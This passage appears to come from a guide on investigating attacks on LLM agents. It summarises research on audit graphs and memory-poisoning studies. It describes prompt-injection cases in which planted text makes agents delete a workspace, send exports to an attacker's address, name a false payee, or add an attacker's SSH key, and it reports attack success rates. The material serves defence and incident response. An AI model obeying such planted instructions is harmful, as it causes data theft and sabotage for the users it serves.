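Investigators often have to combine an inventory of tools, a log of actions and a history of the agent's memory. *Towards Security-Auditable LLM Agents* (Li, Zhang et al., 2026) proposes putting these into one graph, called Agent-BOM. The name refers to a software bill of materials, which lists a program's components.

The graph has one layer for lasting components, such as models, tools, standing instructions and long-term memory. A second layer holds the events of each session, including outside inputs, goals, reasoning, decisions and actions. Links between the layers show, for example, which action wrote a memory and which later session read it. Each item can also include details such as its source, whether anyone altered it and whether the user confirmed the action.

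An audit has four stages: finding a suspicious item, tracing it back to its origin, tracing it forward to its effects, and checking the whole path against a rule. The forward trace covers the later damage that AgentTracer can miss.

In one demonstration, an attacker gave the agent a command to delete its workspace, disguised as a maintenance rule. The agent saved the command to long-term memory, retrieved it in a later session and deleted the workspace. The graph connected the deletion to the memory entry, and the memory entry to the attacker's original input.

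The evidence for Agent-BOM is mainly four such staged scenarios, and Li, Zhang and colleagues report no accuracy rates for them. Agent-BOM did poorly in Yao and colleagues' comparison, although that may partly reflect how they reproduced or configured it. Its design is still a useful guide to which records a team should connect. But Agent-BOM needs more detailed records than many agents keep, and a missing memory write would break the path.

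### When the planting and the effect are in different sessions

In the earlier example of a poisoned memory, an agent saves a false export address from an attacker's ticket in March and sends another employee's export there in April. A search that starts at the last user request before the upload excludes the ticket, because that request was made in April.

Xie, Zhu and colleagues (2026), in *What If Prompt Injection Never Left?*, divide such attacks into four stages. Each one leaves a different record:

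| Stage | In the export example | Evidence |
|---|---|---|
| Injection | The agent reads the attacker's ticket | The tool result from March |
| Persistence | The agent saves the false address | The call that wrote the note, or a comparison of the memory before and after |
| Incorporation | The April session loads the note | A record of which note the agent retrieved |
| Activation | The agent sends the export to the false address | The tool call and its arguments |

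The stored note may be a summary or paraphrase of the ticket, so searching old logs for its exact words can fail. A destination address is a better search term, because the attack works only if the rewriting preserves the address. If the log records each note's identifier and the session that wrote it, the investigator can find the March session without searching for text.

Xie and colleagues tested 486 of these attacks, and about 42% succeeded from start to finish. Attempts to plant false facts succeeded 74% of the time, compared with 36% for attempts to cause unwanted actions and 7% for attempts to change preferences. A false fact can be especially hard to trace because the agent may repeat it in an answer without making an unusual tool call.

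The later session may not raise an alert. *MemHarmBench* (Wang, Feng et al., 2026) gives the example of an imported note that tells an agent to name Harbor Clearing as the recipient in future expense summaries. Somebody deletes the note after the agent has saved the rule. When the user later asks for a summary of an expense report, the agent completes the task normally but names Harbor Clearing instead of the correct recipient, Northstar Travel.

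In tests, agents that had stored such a rule made the choice the attacker wanted, while completing the user's task with no visible fault, in an average of 56% of later sessions. Investigators therefore can't rely on loops, errors or unfinished tasks to reveal the effects. The tests made the rule easier to plant by asking the agent to adopt a workflow convention, so the figure doesn't measure how often an ordinary document would enter memory.

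AgentTracer could be extended to handle traces that end at a memory entry. It would search for the call that created or changed the entry, build a graph of the earlier session containing that call, and join the two graphs. Yao and colleagues tried this on 45 of Xie and colleagues' cases and found the injection point in more than 85% of them. They left the result out of their formal evaluation because the sample was too small and covered too few situations.

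### Recovering after a confirmed attack

The team needs the trace to work out what to undo. Revoking a stolen key is the right response to OPS-214, but in the release-page attack the team has to remove the key the attacker added. Replacing the owner's key would leave the attacker's working. The team should examine repository activity since the agent registered the key, because the attacker could have copied or changed code. It also needs to replace any passwords or login codes in the emails the agent read.

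To clean the memory, the team should find every session in which an agent read the note with the false export address, and every note written in those sessions. An agent may have copied the address into a summary, which would remain if the team deleted only the original note. Restoring the memory from before the March session is simpler, but it loses the legitimate notes saved since then. After either repair, the team can repeat the April request in an isolated copy of the system and check which address the agent uses.

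The original ticket or web page may have reached other agents. The team should search session logs, memory and document stores for its identifier or address, distinctive phrases from the planted text, and anything the attacker needed to keep unchanged, such as the destination or the added SSH key. The team should also check sessions where an agent read the text but the log shows no harmful action, because the agent may have saved the instruction for later. If the planted text is on somebody else's website, the team can block its own agents from the page and notify the owner.

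The team can then use the confirmed attack to improve the detector. For the release-page attack, they could write a rule that raises an alert when an agent adds an SSH key that the user did not request, and test it for false alarms on a harmless session in which the user did ask for a new key. Cross-session attacks need test cases that include both sessions and the memory between them, because a detector that reads only the April export may have no evidence that the address came from an attacker.
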